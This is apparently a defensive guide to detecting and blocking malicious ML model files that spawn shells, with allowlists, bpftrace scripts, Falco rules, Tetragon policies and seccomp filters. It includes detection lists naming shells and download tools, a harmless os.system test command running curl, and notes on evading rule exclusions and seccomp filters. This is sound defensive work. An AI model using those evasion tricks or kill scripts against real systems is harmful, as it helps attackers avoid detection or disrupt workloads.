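The commands in the top row are Elastic's example of a typical attack in its investigation guide, and they only just reach the threshold. `whoami` and `uname` count as the same kind. The search for environment commands matches "env" followed by a space, so a bare `env` is counted under everything else, but `python3 -m venv /opt/app` matches because "venv" ends in "env".

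This rule is a poor fit for detecting malicious model files. A pickle instruction that calls os.system once starts one shell from Python, whatever that shell goes on to do. If it opens a reverse shell, the rule doesn't count the attacker's later commands, because the shell starts them rather than Python. The rule can also miss a burst that crosses from one clock minute to the next, since six commands may be split into three in each minute.

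The rule can catch a Python backdoor that receives commands one at a time and opens a new shell for each. It can do so without any history or list of permitted programs, even on a machine where a single shell is not evidence of an attack. Its false alarm rate is less clear. Elastic tags its noise level as "Unknown", and the notebook example shows that a user could trigger it by running all the cells in a set-up notebook.

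### An allowlist for each container image

A container image is the packaged set of files from which containers start. All containers from one image have the same programs and libraries, so their normal child processes should be very similar. An operator can list the permitted program starts for each image and report any others.

For a speech-recognition server, the list might be short:

| Parent | Permitted child |
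|---|---|
| /usr/local/bin/python3.14 | /usr/local/bin/python3.14 |
| /usr/local/bin/python3.14 | /sbin/ldconfig |
| /usr/local/bin/python3.14 | /usr/bin/uname |
| /usr/local/bin/python3.14 | /usr/bin/ffmpeg |

Both program starts in the test case violate this list, because Python may not start a shell and nothing may start curl. The list also catches a renamed copy of curl, a Perl script and any program that ffmpeg starts.

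An allowlist's weak point is that an attacker can misuse the programs it permits. ffmpeg can read from network addresses as well as local files, and a list that included git would let an attacker download a repository. Checking arguments helps, and for a shell they should match exactly. If an old version of Python needs `sh -c "uname -p"`, the entry should permit only that command, because a wildcard at the end would also permit `uname -p; curl ...`.

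To build the list of normal child processes, the operator can run the image on a test machine with a trusted model and record which programs the workload starts. The test should include a cold start, the first request, a restart and each type of input, since a compiler or ffmpeg may run only in some of these cases. Recording in production is easier and gives better coverage, but any programs an attacker started during the recording would end up on the list. The reviewer should be able to explain why each entry is there.

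The main drawback of this method is that every new version of the image needs another test. It works well for inference servers, passably for training jobs and hardly at all for notebooks. A stricter version uses separate lists for loading and inference. In Falco, the list entries can be written as exceptions to a general rule.

### Why a small error rate can still produce too many alerts

Intrusions are so rare compared with ordinary program starts that even a very accurate detection rule is hard to use. As an illustration, if an organisation runs 1,000 containers that each start 20 child processes a day, a rule that wrongly flags 0.1% of the harmless ones will raise about 1,800 false alerts in 90 days. If there is one real intrusion in that time and the rule catches it, staff would have to find that alert among the 1,800 false ones.

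- Program starts per day: 1,000 × 20 = 20,000
- False alerts per day: 20,000 × 0.001 = 20
- False alerts in 90 days: 20 × 90 = 1,800
- Precision, the share of alerts that are real: 1 / 1,801, or about 0.06%

The rule correctly ignores 99.9% of harmless program starts, yet 1,800 of its 1,801 alerts are false. Checking the alerts at ten minutes each takes more than three hours a day, and the person doing it will probably have stopped looking closely by the time the real one arrives. Better detection of attacks can't fix this, because the rule already catches the only attack. For half of its alerts to be real, it could wrongly flag only one harmless program start in 1.8 million.

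An allowlist for each image helps because false alerts often share a cause. For example, a logger that runs git once a day in each of 20 containers can cause 20 false alerts a day, and a single allowlist entry removes them all.

Suppose the 1,000 containers come from 20 images, with 50 containers per image, and the lists cover every program the images currently start. New false alerts then come mainly from updates. If each image is updated six times in 90 days, there are 120 updates. If a quarter of them each add one harmless program that isn't on the list, there are 30 new programs to review. Each program runs in 50 containers, and we assume it raises one alert per container before someone adds it to the list.

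| Method | False alerts in 90 days | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| Rule that wrongly flags 0.1% of starts | 1,800 | 0.06% |
| Allowlist per image, with an alert from every container | 1,500 | 0.07% |
| The same, with one alert per image and program | 30 | 3.2% |
| The same, after tests before release catch nine in ten new programs | 3 | 25% |

The allowlist alone barely changes the total. Most of the improvement comes from grouping identical alerts and testing each update before release. Thirty false alerts in 90 days is one every three days, which a small team can investigate properly even though precision is still low.

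When alerts are grouped, an operator who dismisses one as a harmless update may not examine the same alert from another container, so the group should keep the arguments and parent process from every container. The fixed list helps operators set priorities. An unlisted shell or download tool deserves attention before an unlisted copy of uname.

All four rows apply only if the intrusion starts a program that the rule can report. If the attacker uses only permitted programs with permitted arguments, the allowlist produces no true alerts, so its precision is zero even if it produces few false ones.

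## The same detection in Falco

Grouping alerts by container image requires knowing which image each process came from, but the bpftrace script prints only a cgroup path. Someone also has to install and maintain the script on every server. Falco does the same detection across a fleet. It collects events from each machine's kernel, adds details about the process and its container, and checks them against rules written in YAML, a common configuration format. The security company Sysdig created Falco in 2016, according to CNCF's *Cloud Native Computing Foundation Announces Falco Graduation* (2024), and Falco's maintainers now include engineers from Amazon, Apple, IBM and Red Hat.

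### From the kernel to an alert

Suppose the model server from the test case runs in a container, and process 4207 has just called execve to become a shell. Falco handles the event in six steps:

1. A driver in the kernel records the call when it returns, including the return value, the program's path and its arguments.
2. The driver writes the record to a buffer, and the Falco process in user space reads it.
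3. Falco's libraries update their process table. They added 4207 when Python created it, with 4100 as its parent, and now change its name from python3 to sh.
4. A plugin identifies the container and gets the image's name from the software that runs it. On Kubernetes, it also gets the name of the pod, the unit in which Kubernetes runs containers.
5. The rule engine tests the event against the rules that cover execve.
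6. If a rule matches, Falco fills in the rule's message and sends the alert.

The process table serves the same purpose as the watch list in the bpftrace script, but it is in user space and covers every process on the machine. When Falco starts, it adds the processes that are already running to the table, so it can follow a model server that started before Falco did. It used to read this information from /proc, the directory in which the kernel describes running processes. According to the Falco 0.44.0 release notes, the eBPF driver can now collect it inside the kernel, which is faster.

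Falco uses the same lookup to repair the table after it loses events. If it misses the record of the shell creating process 4208, it can look that process up later, but only while it still exists. A short curl command may have finished by then. Falco would have a record of curl starting but no record of its ancestors, so a rule that requires a Python ancestor wouldn't match.

### Supported drivers and fields

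Falco 0.44.0 came out on 26 May 2026, according to *github falcosecurity/falco 0.44.0* (2026). It supports two drivers on live systems, the "modern" eBPF probe and a kernel module. The eBPF probe uses CO-RE, so one build works on many kernels. The kernel module is for kernels too old for the probe. The eBPF probe is the better choice wherever it works, because the verifier doesn't check kernel modules and a bug in one can crash the machine.

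Falco 0.44.0 removed an older eBPF probe that needed a separate build for each kernel version, and Falco won't start if its configuration still contains that probe's settings. Drivers from 0.43.0 don't work with 0.44.0, so operators have to upgrade the driver and the main program together. On Kubernetes, the `driver.kind=auto` setting in the Helm chart (Falco's installation package) selects a suitable driver for each machine (Douglas, 2024).

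The same release removed support for gVisor, so an organisation that used Falco to monitor gVisor containers has to stay on an older version or send gVisor's events to another monitor.

Some older rules also use outdated fields. Falco used to record the beginning and end of a system call as separate events, and rules selected the end with `evt.dir = <`. Falco has warned about rules that use `evt.dir` since version 0.42, and about those that use the `evt.latency` fields since 0.43. The `evt.dir = <` condition is still common in tutorials, including iximiuz Labs' *Lesson in Kubelings*, and operators should delete it from rules they copy.

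The fields that identified container health checks no longer work. Health checks often run a shell or curl inside the container every few seconds, so a rule that used these fields to exclude them could start producing many alerts. According to the release notes, two of the three kinds of check only ever worked with Docker, and for more than six years they had failed silently on the container software that most Kubernetes clusters use.

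### The parts of a rule

A Falco rule has a name, a description, a condition, an output message and a priority, which ranges from debug to emergency. A list is a named set of values, such as the names of shells. A macro is a named piece of a condition that several rules can share. Exceptions describe events that match the condition but shouldn't raise an alert.

Most rules about program starts use the macro `spawned_process`, which Falco's *Default Macros* defines as follows:

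```yaml
- macro: spawned_process
  condition: (evt.type in (execve, execveat))
```

Despite its name, the macro doesn't check whether the call succeeded. According to its description, one default rule that uses the macro also matches failed attempts. A process keeps its old name after a failed call, so if a shell tries to start a missing program, a rule that matches shells may report the existing shell as a new one. Adding the condition `evt.rawres >= 0` prevents this by testing the return value.

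A rule can test the new program and any of its ancestors. Falco's *Supported Fields for Conditions and Outputs* explains the numbering, in which 1 is the parent and 2 the grandparent. When curl starts in the test case, the fields have these values:

| Field | Value |
|---|---|
| proc.name | curl |
| proc.exepath | /usr/bin/curl |
| proc.pname | sh |
| proc.aname[2] | python3 |
| proc.apid[2] | 4100 |

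In a condition, an ancestor field without a number matches any ancestor, so `proc.aname = python3` is true for both the shell and curl. A condition on `proc.pname` would match only the shell.

### What the default rules would report

Falco's maintainers sort their rules by maturity. Of the 90 rules in July 2025, 25 were stable, 31 incubating, 30 sandbox and 4 deprecated (Falco, 2025). Falco loads only the stable rules by default. Operators have to install the incubating and sandbox rules themselves and may need to adapt them first. The maintainers have since moved the deprecated rules to an archive.

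The table applies the closest rules in Falco's *Default Rules* to the test case, running inside a container.

| Rule | Maturity | Alert? | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| Terminal shell in container | Stable | No | The server has no terminal, and Python is the shell's parent |
| Run shell untrusted | Stable | No | Python isn't on the list of parents it covers |
| Drop and execute new binary in container | Stable | No | sh and curl are part of the image |
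| Redirect STDOUT/STDIN to Network Connection in Container | Stable | No | The shell doesn't use a network connection for input or output |
| Launch Ingress Remote File Copy Tools in Container | Incubating | No | It covers curl only when curl saves a file |
| Web Server Spawned Shell | Sandbox | Probably not | It is meant for servers such as nginx and Apache |

A default installation of Falco would therefore miss the test case. The "Terminal shell in container" rule doesn't catch it because that rule is meant for people who open a shell in a container, for instance with `kubectl exec`. It requires a terminal and a shell that the container software started directly, and a shell from `os.system` meets neither requirement.

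The rule "Run shell untrusted" comes closest to what we need. It detects shells running under applications that shouldn't start them, mainly web, database and mail servers. An operator could add Python to the list of applications, but the rule would then cover every Python program on every machine, including build jobs and notebooks.

Other stable rules can still catch an attack that goes further than the test case. If malicious code connects a shell's input and output to a network socket, the redirection rule raises an alert, even if Python makes the connection before the shell starts. If the code downloads and runs a program, or copies curl to a new name and runs the copy, "Drop and execute new binary in container" reports it at critical priority. That rule detects programs in the writable layer that the container software places over the image. It doesn't cover programs saved in a mounted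 volume, which model servers often have for downloaded models.

The sandbox rule for web servers is a poor template for a Python rule because its exclusions are too broad. It excludes any command line that begins with `sh -c /usr/bin`, so an attacker can avoid detection by writing `/usr/bin/curl` instead of `curl`. It also excludes any command that contains the word "healthcheck", which an attacker can add in a comment.

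### A rule for model servers

The rule below reports any shell or download tool that descends from a Python process in two named images. It needs Falco 0.44.0 or later because it uses `anyof`, a new operator that compares a field with several values.

```yaml
- list: model_server_images
  items: [registry.example.com/speech-api, registry.example.com/text-api]

- list: shells_and_download_tools
  items: [sh, dash, bash, ash, zsh, busybox, curl, wget]

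- macro: shell_or_download_tool
  condition: >
    (proc.name in (shells_and_download_tools) or
    proc.exepath endswith anyof (/dash, /bash, /busybox, /curl, /wget))

- rule: Python Model Server Started Shell or Download Tool
  desc: >
    A descendant of Python in a model-serving container started
    a shell or a tool that fetches files from the network.
  condition: >
    spawned_process and evt.rawres >= 0
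    and container.image.repository in (model_server_images)
    and proc.aexepath contains "/bin/python"
    and shell_or_download_tool
  exceptions:
    - name: known_commands
      fields: [container.image.repository, proc.pexepath, proc.exepath, proc.cmdline]
      values:
        - [registry.example.com/speech-api, /usr/local/bin/python3.8,
           /usr/bin/dash, "sh -c uname -p"]
  output: >
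    Shell or download tool below Python |
    image=%container.image.repository pod=%k8s.pod.name
    process=%proc.name exe=%proc.exepath pid=%proc.pid vpid=%proc.vpid
    parent=%proc.pname gparent=%proc.aname[2] command=%proc.cmdline
  priority: WARNING
  tags: [container, process]
```

The image names don't include version tags, so the rule still applies after an update. The rule looks for Python in the paths of the ancestor processes' program files rather than in the process names, so it also covers a server started through a command such as `vllm`.

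The macro tests both the name and the path of the new program because each test catches programs that the other misses. In a BusyBox container, wget has the name `wget` but the path `/bin/busybox`. If an attacker starts curl through a symbolic link called `helper`, the name is `helper` but the path still ends in `/curl`.

The rule evaluates the two program starts in the test case like this:

| Test | sh, process 4207 | curl, process 4208 |
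|---|---|---|
| Did the call succeed? | Yes | Yes |
| Is the image on the list? | Yes | Yes |
| Is Python an ancestor? | Yes, the parent | Yes, the grandparent |
| Is it a shell or download tool? | Yes | Yes |
| Does the exception apply? | No | No |
| Result | Alert | Alert |

The messages should look roughly like this, with line breaks added:

```
Shell or download tool below Python | image=registry.example.com/speech-api
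  pod=speech-api-0 process=sh exe=/usr/bin/dash pid=4207 vpid=7
  parent=python3 gparent=containerd-shim
  command=sh -c curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done
Shell or download tool below Python | image=registry.example.com/speech-api
  pod=speech-api-0 process=curl exe=/usr/bin/curl pid=4208 vpid=8
  parent=sh gparent=python3
  command=curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/
```

`pid` is the process's number on the host and `vpid` is its number inside the container.

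The exception permits the `uname -p` command that old versions of Python run through a shell. Falco adds an exception to the condition with "and not", and this one applies only if all four values match exactly. The values include the shell's path because `proc.cmdline` begins with the process name, so an attacker could produce the same command line by running a different program from a file called `sh`.

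Most health checks don't need an exception. The container software starts them, so they usually have no Python ancestor, even when they run a shell and curl in the same container. A health check written in Python that calls curl would need an exception.

The ancestor condition also makes the rule miss some attacks. If malicious code replaces the Python process with a shell without creating a child, the new shell has no Python ancestor. The bpftrace script catches this because its watch list records that the process used to be Python. Background processes can also lose their Python ancestor if the shell that created them exits first. Their new parent is usually the container's first process. The rule still detects them if that process is Python, but not if it is a small program that only starts the server.

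If nothing in an image should ever run a shell, the operator can close both gaps by removing the ancestor condition. The rule would then also report health checks, start-up scripts and administrators who open a shell in the container.

When several rules match an event, Falco by default raises an alert only for the one it loaded first. If a matching default rule loads before the custom rule, the operator gets the default rule's message instead. The Helm settings in *Default Rules* avoid this by loading the directory for custom rules, `/etc/falco/rules.d`, before the default system-call rules.

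### Testing the rule

Falco can check the file without starting to monitor. The rule depends on a macro from the default rules, so the command has to include both files:

```
falco -V /etc/falco/falco_rules.yaml -V /etc/falco/rules.d/model-servers.yaml
```

Version 0.44.0 also rejects unknown keys in rules, macros and lists. Earlier versions silently ignored them, so if someone misspelled `exceptions`, Falco would load the rule without its exceptions.

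The next step is to run the test command inside a container from one of the listed images, here called `speech`:

```
docker exec speech python3 -c 'import os; os.system("curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/; echo done")'
```

Inside a container, 127.0.0.1 usually refers to the container itself, where nothing may be listening on port 8000. The test still works, because curl has to start before it can fail to connect. Several other commands are worth trying in the same way:

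| Action by Python in the container | Expected alerts |
|---|---|
| Run `uname -p` through os.system, in the image with the exception | None |
| Run `uname -p; curl -s http://127.0.0.1:8000/` in the same image | Two |
| Start curl through the subprocess module, without a shell | One |
| Run the original test command in an image that isn't listed | None |
| Replace Python with curl through os.execvp | None, because of the gap described above |

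Falco's separate event-generator program can automate such tests. Since event-generator 0.13.0, an operator can describe a series of steps in YAML, including a chain of processes, and name the rule that should match. `event-generator suite test` then performs the steps and reports whether the rule matched. Falco can download new versions of the default rules automatically, and a change to a shared macro such as `spawned_process` would also change the custom rule, so the tests are worth repeating after each rule update as well as each Falco upgrade.

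Falco can also record the events around an alert in a capture file and later run rules on the recording. If an alert turns out to be false, the operator can write an exception and test it on the original events without reproducing them. Capture files can grow quickly, and Falco 0.44.0 added a size limit, `capture.max_file_size_mb`. The files may also contain private data from the workload, so they need the same protection as the server's logs.

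### Using bpftrace and Falco together

bpftrace is better for investigating a single host or trying out a condition. It can read almost any field in the kernel's data structures, and a change takes effect as soon as the operator restarts the script. Falco can use only the fields its developers have provided, but it adds container and Kubernetes data and delivers alerts from every machine in the same format. It makes sense to develop an idea in bpftrace and move it to Falco once it works.

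For example, an operator may want to add git to the list of download tools. The bpftrace script records every program that descends from Python, so a day of its output from one busy server shows how often git starts and what starts it. If an experiment logger runs git at the start of every job, the Falco rule will need an exception for that before the operator deploys the rule to the other machines.

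The bpftrace script can also clarify an ambiguous Falco alert. Falco joins a program's arguments with spaces, so `sh -c "uname -p"` and `sh -c uname -p` look the same, although the shell treats `-p` differently in each. The script distinguishes them by printing a zero byte between arguments. To investigate a recurring suspicious command, an engineer can run the script on the affected host and match its records with Falco's by time and host pid.

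bpftrace and Falco can run at the same time. They have separate buffers, so a slow bpftrace script doesn't cause Falco to lose events, but each adds work to every program start. If the operator has installed Falco's incubating rules, starting bpftrace will probably trigger "BPF Program Not Profiled", which reports programs that load eBPF code. The operator can add bpftrace to the rule's list of known programs, but on a production server it may be better to keep the alert, because an attacker with root access could use bpftrace too.

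Running the bpftrace script alongside Falco for an hour is also a good check on Falco. If the script marks a shell in a listed image as `ALERT` and Falco reports nothing, the rule has a gap, the event matched an exception or another rule, or Falco lost an event.

### Lost events and alert delivery

Falco usually handles far more events than a monitor that traces only execve, because its default rules also cover file access and network connections. Its load is therefore closer to that of the busy monitor in the earlier buffer calculation. Falco reports the number of events and drops for each processor core, listed in the Falco (2024) release notes as `n_evts_cpu` and `n_drops_cpu`. The operator should set an alert for any increase in drops. A machine that only serves models may not need all the default rules, and disabling some can reduce the number of events Falco collects.

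Falco can write alerts to a file or the system log, or send them over HTTP. A companion program, Falcosidekick, forwards them to many other services. Falco 0.44.0 removed the gRPC output, which also sent alerts over the network, so systems that still rely on it need a replacement before they upgrade.

When `json_output` is enabled, Falco sends each alert as structured data. `output_fields` contains only the fields in the rule's output message, so an operator who leaves out the image name can't search for it later. Elastic's *Falco Integration* has the same limitation because it receives only what Falco sends. Including the command line helps explain an alert, but it may contain a password or access token that shouldn't be in a shared log.

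The log system is a good place to group alerts by image and program, as the previous section recommended. A ready-made search from Splunk counts alerts from Falco's terminal-shell rule by image, container, parent process and user. It looks for the phrase "A shell was spawned in a container", so it would miss alerts from the custom rule and would stop working if someone reworded the message. Searching for the rule's name is more reliable.

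A lack of alerts can also mean that Falco isn't running. The release notes for Falco 0.44.0 describe a bug in the container plugin that made Falco crash repeatedly on machines with containerd 2.3.0, the software that runs containers on many Kubernetes clusters. A daily job can run the harmless test command on each machine, and the log system can warn the operator if the expected alert doesn't arrive.

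### Tracee as an alternative

Aqua Security's Tracee also uses eBPF to monitor whole machines and containers. Its main advantage for this job is the detail in its program-start event. According to Aqua Security's *sched process exec*, the event includes the command path, the executable path, a script's interpreter, the arguments and the environment variables. It also includes the file's inode number and creation time, which can help an investigator tell whether a program came with the image or was added later. Like the bpftrace script, the event leaves out failed attempts.

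Tracee may suit a team that expects to investigate incidents in depth. Falco's rule language is enough for a permanent alert on a few kinds of program start, and Falco's existing rules cover some of what an attacker might do next. Both tools mainly report events after they happen, whereas Tetragon, another eBPF tool, can also kill the process.

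## Stopping the process as well as reporting it

In the test case, the shell runs while the monitor is still reading its record and checking the rules, so the alert always comes after the program has started. By the time a person reads the alert, both the shell and curl have probably exited.

Stopping the attack therefore needs an automatic response, and the earlier it acts, the less the attacker can do.

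### Four responses

| Response | When it acts | Does the shell run? | Result of os.system |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kill from user space | Milliseconds to seconds after the program start | Yes | Depends on whether the shell has finished |
| Signal from an eBPF program | Before execve returns to user space | No | Killed by signal 9 |
| Refusal at the LSM hook | Before the kernel replaces the program | No | Exit status 127 |
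| Seccomp filter | On entry to the system call | No | Exit status 127 |

(The last column assumes the GNU C library.)

**Killing from user space.** A program that receives the alert can send SIGKILL, the signal that ends a process immediately, to process 4207. This is easy to add to any monitor, but killing the shell doesn't kill curl, which is a separate process. If the shell has already exited, Linux may have reused 4207 for an unrelated process, so the program should compare the process's start time with the alert before sending the signal. On Linux 5.14 and later, writing 1 to the `cgroup.kill` file of the container's cgroup kills every process in the container, including both curl and the model server.

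An eBPF program can send SIGKILL itself while the process is still inside execve. The kernel marks the signal as pending, finishes the system call and checks for pending signals just before it returns to user space. If the program sends the signal at the end of execve, the kernel has already loaded the shell, but the process dies before the shell's first instruction runs. Tetragon's *Policy Enforcement* describes the same behaviour for system calls in general, where the killed application never returns from the call.

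A kill signal that arrives late is less useful against some other system calls than against execve, because a completed execve does little harm if the new program never runs. Tetragon's *Enforcement* gives the example of a write, where the data may still reach the file even though the process is killed during the call.

**Refusal at the LSM hook.** An eBPF program at `bprm_check_security` can return an error, and the kernel then abandons the call. This one refuses every program start by a process on the `watched` list from the first eBPF example:

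```c
SEC("lsm/bprm_check_security")
int BPF_PROG(refuse_start, struct linux_binprm *bprm)
{
    __u32 pid = bpf_get_current_pid_tgid() >> 32;
    return bpf_map_lookup_elem(&watched, &pid) ? -EPERM : 0;
}
```

The kernel needs the build option `CONFIG_BPF_LSM=y`, and `bpf` has to appear in `/sys/kernel/security/lsm`. If `bpf` is missing, the operator has to change the boot settings and restart the machine, according to Tetragon's *Tracing Policy*.

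**Seccomp filter.** A server that never needs another program can give up execve altogether. It can't usually do this through a container-wide seccomp profile, because the container software applies the profile before it starts Python, and starting Python takes an execve. The server has to install the filter itself, before it loads the model. With the Python module from libseccomp, that takes a few lines:

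```python
import errno, seccomp

f = seccomp.SyscallFilter(defaction=seccomp.ALLOW)
for call in ("execve", "execveat"):
    f.add_rule(seccomp.ERRNO(errno.EPERM), call)
f.load()
```

Code in a malicious model file can't remove the filter once it is installed, but may be able to get around it. By default, the filter covers only the thread that installs it and any threads or processes that thread creates later. If Python has already started a `forkserver` process, for example, malicious code could use that process to create an unfiltered worker. The server should therefore install the filter before it starts any threads or helper processes. Features that need to run another program, such as `torch.compile` on a CPU, will then fail.

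When an LSM or a seccomp filter blocks an `execve` call, no program starts, so `sched_process_exec` doesn't fire. The attempt still appears at `sys_exit_execve` with a return value of −1, and the monitor should report it.

None of the last three responses removes the malicious code from Python. When `os.system` fails, process 4100 keeps running, and the code can still open a network connection itself. A blocked shell is a reason to investigate the server and probably replace it.

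### A script that can kill the wrong process

cr0nx (2024) published a short bpftrace script that kills programs started by network services, and suggested it as a stopgap for vulnerable servers. It has two probes:

1. When any process calls execve, the first probe copies the caller's comm into a variable named `@parent`.
2. When an execve call returns, the second probe compares `@parent` with a list of five service names, including httpd and php-fpm. If one matches, the probe prints a message and sends SIGKILL to the process that made the call.

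The script saves the caller's name at entry because comm has changed by the time execve returns. But `@parent` is a single variable shared by every processor core, so two program starts at the same time overwrite each other's value. Suppose an administrator logs in just as an attacker makes the web server start a shell:

| Step | Core | Event | `@parent` | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | sshd's child calls execve for bash | sshd | |
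| 2 | 1 | httpd's child calls execve for sh | httpd | |
| 3 | 0 | The call for bash returns | httpd | Kills the administrator's shell |
| 4 | 1 | The call for sh returns | httpd | Kills the attacker's shell |

The problem is worse because `httpd` appears in the log as the source of both processes. If step 2 happens before step 1, `@parent` contains `sshd` at both returns and the attacker's shell keeps running.

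Overlapping execve calls needn't be rare. If each call takes 1 millisecond and the machine makes 20 calls a second, another call begins before a given one finishes about 2% of the time (20 × 0.001). During a software build with 1,000 calls a second, this happens about 63% of the time.

The repair is to store one name per thread:

```
tracepoint:syscalls:sys_enter_exec*
{
    @caller[tid] = comm;
}

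tracepoint:syscalls:sys_exit_exec*
{
    $caller = @caller[tid];
    delete(@caller, tid);

    if (args.ret == 0 && ($caller == "httpd" || $caller == "php-fpm")) {
        printf("killing pid=%d caller=%s\n", pid, $caller);
        signal(9);
    }
}
```

The administrator's shell and the attacker's now have separate entries, so the order of events no longer matters. This version also covers execveat. It ignores failed calls, whereas the original kills a process whose first attempt fails during a PATH search.

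The script still has two problems. If a worker thread calls execve, it takes over the main thread's ID, and the lookup at the end finds nothing. The script also kills legitimate program starts. For example, PHP-FPM uses execve to restart itself when an administrator reloads its configuration, so the script would kill the service during a routine reload.

For a model server, it is better to add the kill to the full bpftrace script from earlier, which already handles worker threads and follows ancestry instead of names. The following lines go after its `printf`, so that the script writes the record first:

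```
    if ($known) {
        signal(9);
    }
```

bpftrace only permits `signal` when the operator starts it with `--unsafe`.

Errors in the watch list matter more once the monitor can kill processes. A leftover entry for a dead process would cause a false alert in a monitor that only reports, but it could make a monitor that kills processes stop an unrelated one that reuses the process ID. A compiled eBPF program can avoid this with task-local storage, which Cui and colleagues use in one version of their monitor. Task-local storage attaches the data to the kernel's record of the process, and the kernel discards both together.

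### The same policy in Tetragon

Tetragon is an open-source eBPF tool, built mainly for Kubernetes, that can block operations as well as report them. An operator writes a policy in YAML that names a point in the kernel, the conditions to check there and the action to take. Tetragon checks the conditions and acts inside the kernel, so it doesn't have to wait for a user-space program.

This policy refuses every program start by Python or its descendants in pods labelled `speech-api`:

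```yaml
apiVersion: cilium.io/v1alpha1
kind: TracingPolicy
metadata:
  name: "model-server-no-children"
spec:
  podSelector:
    matchLabels:
      app: "speech-api"
  options:
  - name: "policy-mode"
    value: "monitor"
  kprobes:
  - call: "security_bprm_check"
    syscall: false
    args:
    - index: 0
      type: "linux_binprm"
    selectors:
    - matchBinaries:
      - operator: "In"
        values:
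        - "/usr/local/bin/python3.14"
        followChildren: true
      matchActions:
      - action: Override
        argError: -1
```

`security_bprm_check` is the kernel function that runs the LSM hook. The `Override` action skips this function and returns −1 ("operation not permitted") instead. The alternative action, `Sigkill`, kills the process that made the call.

In the test case, either action stops the shell and leaves Python running, because the caller is the child process, 4207. If Python instead calls `os.execv` to replace itself with a shell, the caller is the server, so `Sigkill` ends the server, while `Override` returns an error and the server continues. Tetragon's documentation recommends combining the two when the operation must not complete. That is reasonable for a server that is probably compromised, but in a first deployment `Override` alone does less damage if the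 policy is wrong.

The `followChildren` setting extends the policy from Python to its descendant processes, but Tetragon doesn't apply it to children that existed before the operator installed the policy. A similar gap can occur when a container starts. Tetragon closes it with a hook in the container runtime, and without that hook it applies pod-specific policies only on a best-effort basis.

The policy above starts in `monitor` mode, in which Tetragon reports matches but doesn't carry out the `Override`. After a trial, the operator can switch the policy to `enforce` mode without editing it.

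### What a wrong kill costs

Detection.FYI's *Unusual Child Execution via Web Server*, a copy of an Elastic rule, gives some idea of how often a broad rule would kill the wrong process. It reports unfamiliar child processes of web servers, including gunicorn and uvicorn, which often serve Python models. Elastic tags the rule's noise level as high, even though the rule ignores recently seen combinations, which cr0nx's script does not do.

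The cost of each mistake depends on the workload. Suppose a training job uses 512 GPUs and saves a checkpoint every hour. The GPUs work in step, so if one process dies, the whole job usually stops and has to restart from the last checkpoint. A kill at a random time loses half an hour of work on average:

512 GPUs × 0.5 hours = 256 GPU-hours

The worst case, just before a checkpoint, is 512 GPU-hours. If the job takes 15 minutes to restart, that adds another 128.

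Blocking a program can crash a training job even if the monitor doesn't kill the training process. If the monitor blocks an experiment logger from running nvidia-smi, Python's subprocess module raises an exception, and the job may crash if no code handles it.

An automatic kill is worthwhile if it prevents more damage than false alarms cause in lost work. With 30 false alerts for every real one, the ratio in the earlier example after grouping, stopping one attack loses 30 × 256 = 7,680 GPU-hours, or about $15,000 at an assumed $2 per GPU-hour. With three false alerts per real one, it loses 768 GPU-hours, or about $1,500. Stolen model weights or cloud credentials could easily cost more, so killing training jobs may still be worthwhile. But the expense of wrong kills is a good reason to make the rule precise first and to try less disruptive responses, such as cutting off the job's internet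 access.

Sophos' *Automated response* warns that killing processes can affect how the host works and strongly recommends dry runs before production use. Datadog's *variables and actions* describes a safeguard against kill loops, in which a service keeps restarting and the agent keeps killing it. After too many kills of the same executable or in the same container, the agent temporarily suppresses further kills. An attacker might deliberately trigger kills until this happens, so the suppression should raise an urgent alert.

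### A policy for each kind of machine

| Workload | Unlisted shell or download tool | Other unlisted program |
|---|---|---|
| Inference server | Refuse, alert and replace the server | Alert at first, refuse after a trial |
| Training job, while it loads the model | Refuse and stop the job | Alert |
| Training job, once training is under way | Cut internet access and call someone | Alert |
| Development machine | Alert | Record |

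Inference servers are the workloads best suited to automatic refusal. They need few child processes, and if one server has to stop, another can usually take its requests. But if the rule is wrong, the other servers can't take over, because every server from the same image will fail in the same way. A rule that omitted ffmpeg from the allowed programs would break speech recognition on all of them. The operator should enforce a new rule on one server before the rest.

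The best time to stop a training job is at the start. Malicious code in a model file often runs while the file loads, when the job has little work to lose. Stopping a 512-GPU job after five minutes loses about 43 GPU-hours. Later in the run, cutting internet access limits what an attacker can steal while someone decides whether to stop the job, but the connections between GPUs and to storage have to stay open. If the alert is real, the attacker may have altered a checkpoint saved just before stopping. Restarting from an earlier checkpoint is safer, though it loses more work.

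On a development machine, people often start shells from Python, so automatic kills would mostly interrupt their work. It makes sense to reserve kills there for a narrow pattern, such as a shell connected to an outside address.

### Evidence to save before killing

Killing a process destroys its memory, and Linux removes its entry in `/proc`. If there is time, the operator should freeze the container first by writing 1 to the `cgroup.freeze` file of its cgroup. The processes stop running, but their memory and open files remain. The operator can then collect:

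- the model file and its hash, along with the address it came from
- the alert, including the full arguments, the process ancestry and the image's exact version
- the program that started, from `/proc/4207/exe`, which works even if the attacker has deleted the file
- the open files, network connections and environment variables of the shell and the Python server
- a copy of the Python process's memory, which may contain the code that made the call

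Copying the memory can be slow, since 80 GB takes 80 seconds at 1 GB a second. The copy doesn't include the GPU's own memory. Freezing one process in a training job also makes the other processes wait, and they may time out after several minutes. Memory and environment variables often contain passwords and user data, so access to the evidence should be restricted.

If the monitor kills or blocks the shell inside the kernel, the operator has no running shell to freeze, so the eBPF program has to record what it can at that moment. Tetragon can add the calling program's stack trace to an event and, on kernels with file measurement enabled, a hash of the program that was about to run. The Python process is usually still running, so the operator can freeze it and copy its memory before replacing the server.

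## Allowlists of expected behaviour for loading and inference

Malicious code can steal an SSH key from inside Python without starting a program. To catch this, a monitor has to cover the other system calls that a process makes while loading or running a model, and distinguish normal calls from suspicious ones. Since 2024, researchers have tried searching for a few suspicious calls, training a classifier on harmless models, and writing an allowlist by hand.

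### A short list of suspicious calls

ModelTracer, a tool from 2024, records what happens while a model loads by combining a trace of Python functions with the output of strace, which uses ptrace to print a process's system calls. According to Digregorio and colleagues, it treats calls such as socket, connect, execve and chmod as signs of an attack, along with Python's `exec` and `eval`. In the test case, the execve call for sh would be enough to flag the file.

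Harmless code makes some of these calls too. ModelTracer flags the text classifier `twitter-roberta-base-sentiment.bin`, which contains no payload, because a socket call occurs while it loads. Digregorio and colleagues traced the call to a small network probe. Loading the model makes Python import a library for downloading from Hugging Face, which imports other packages, and one of those runs the probe.

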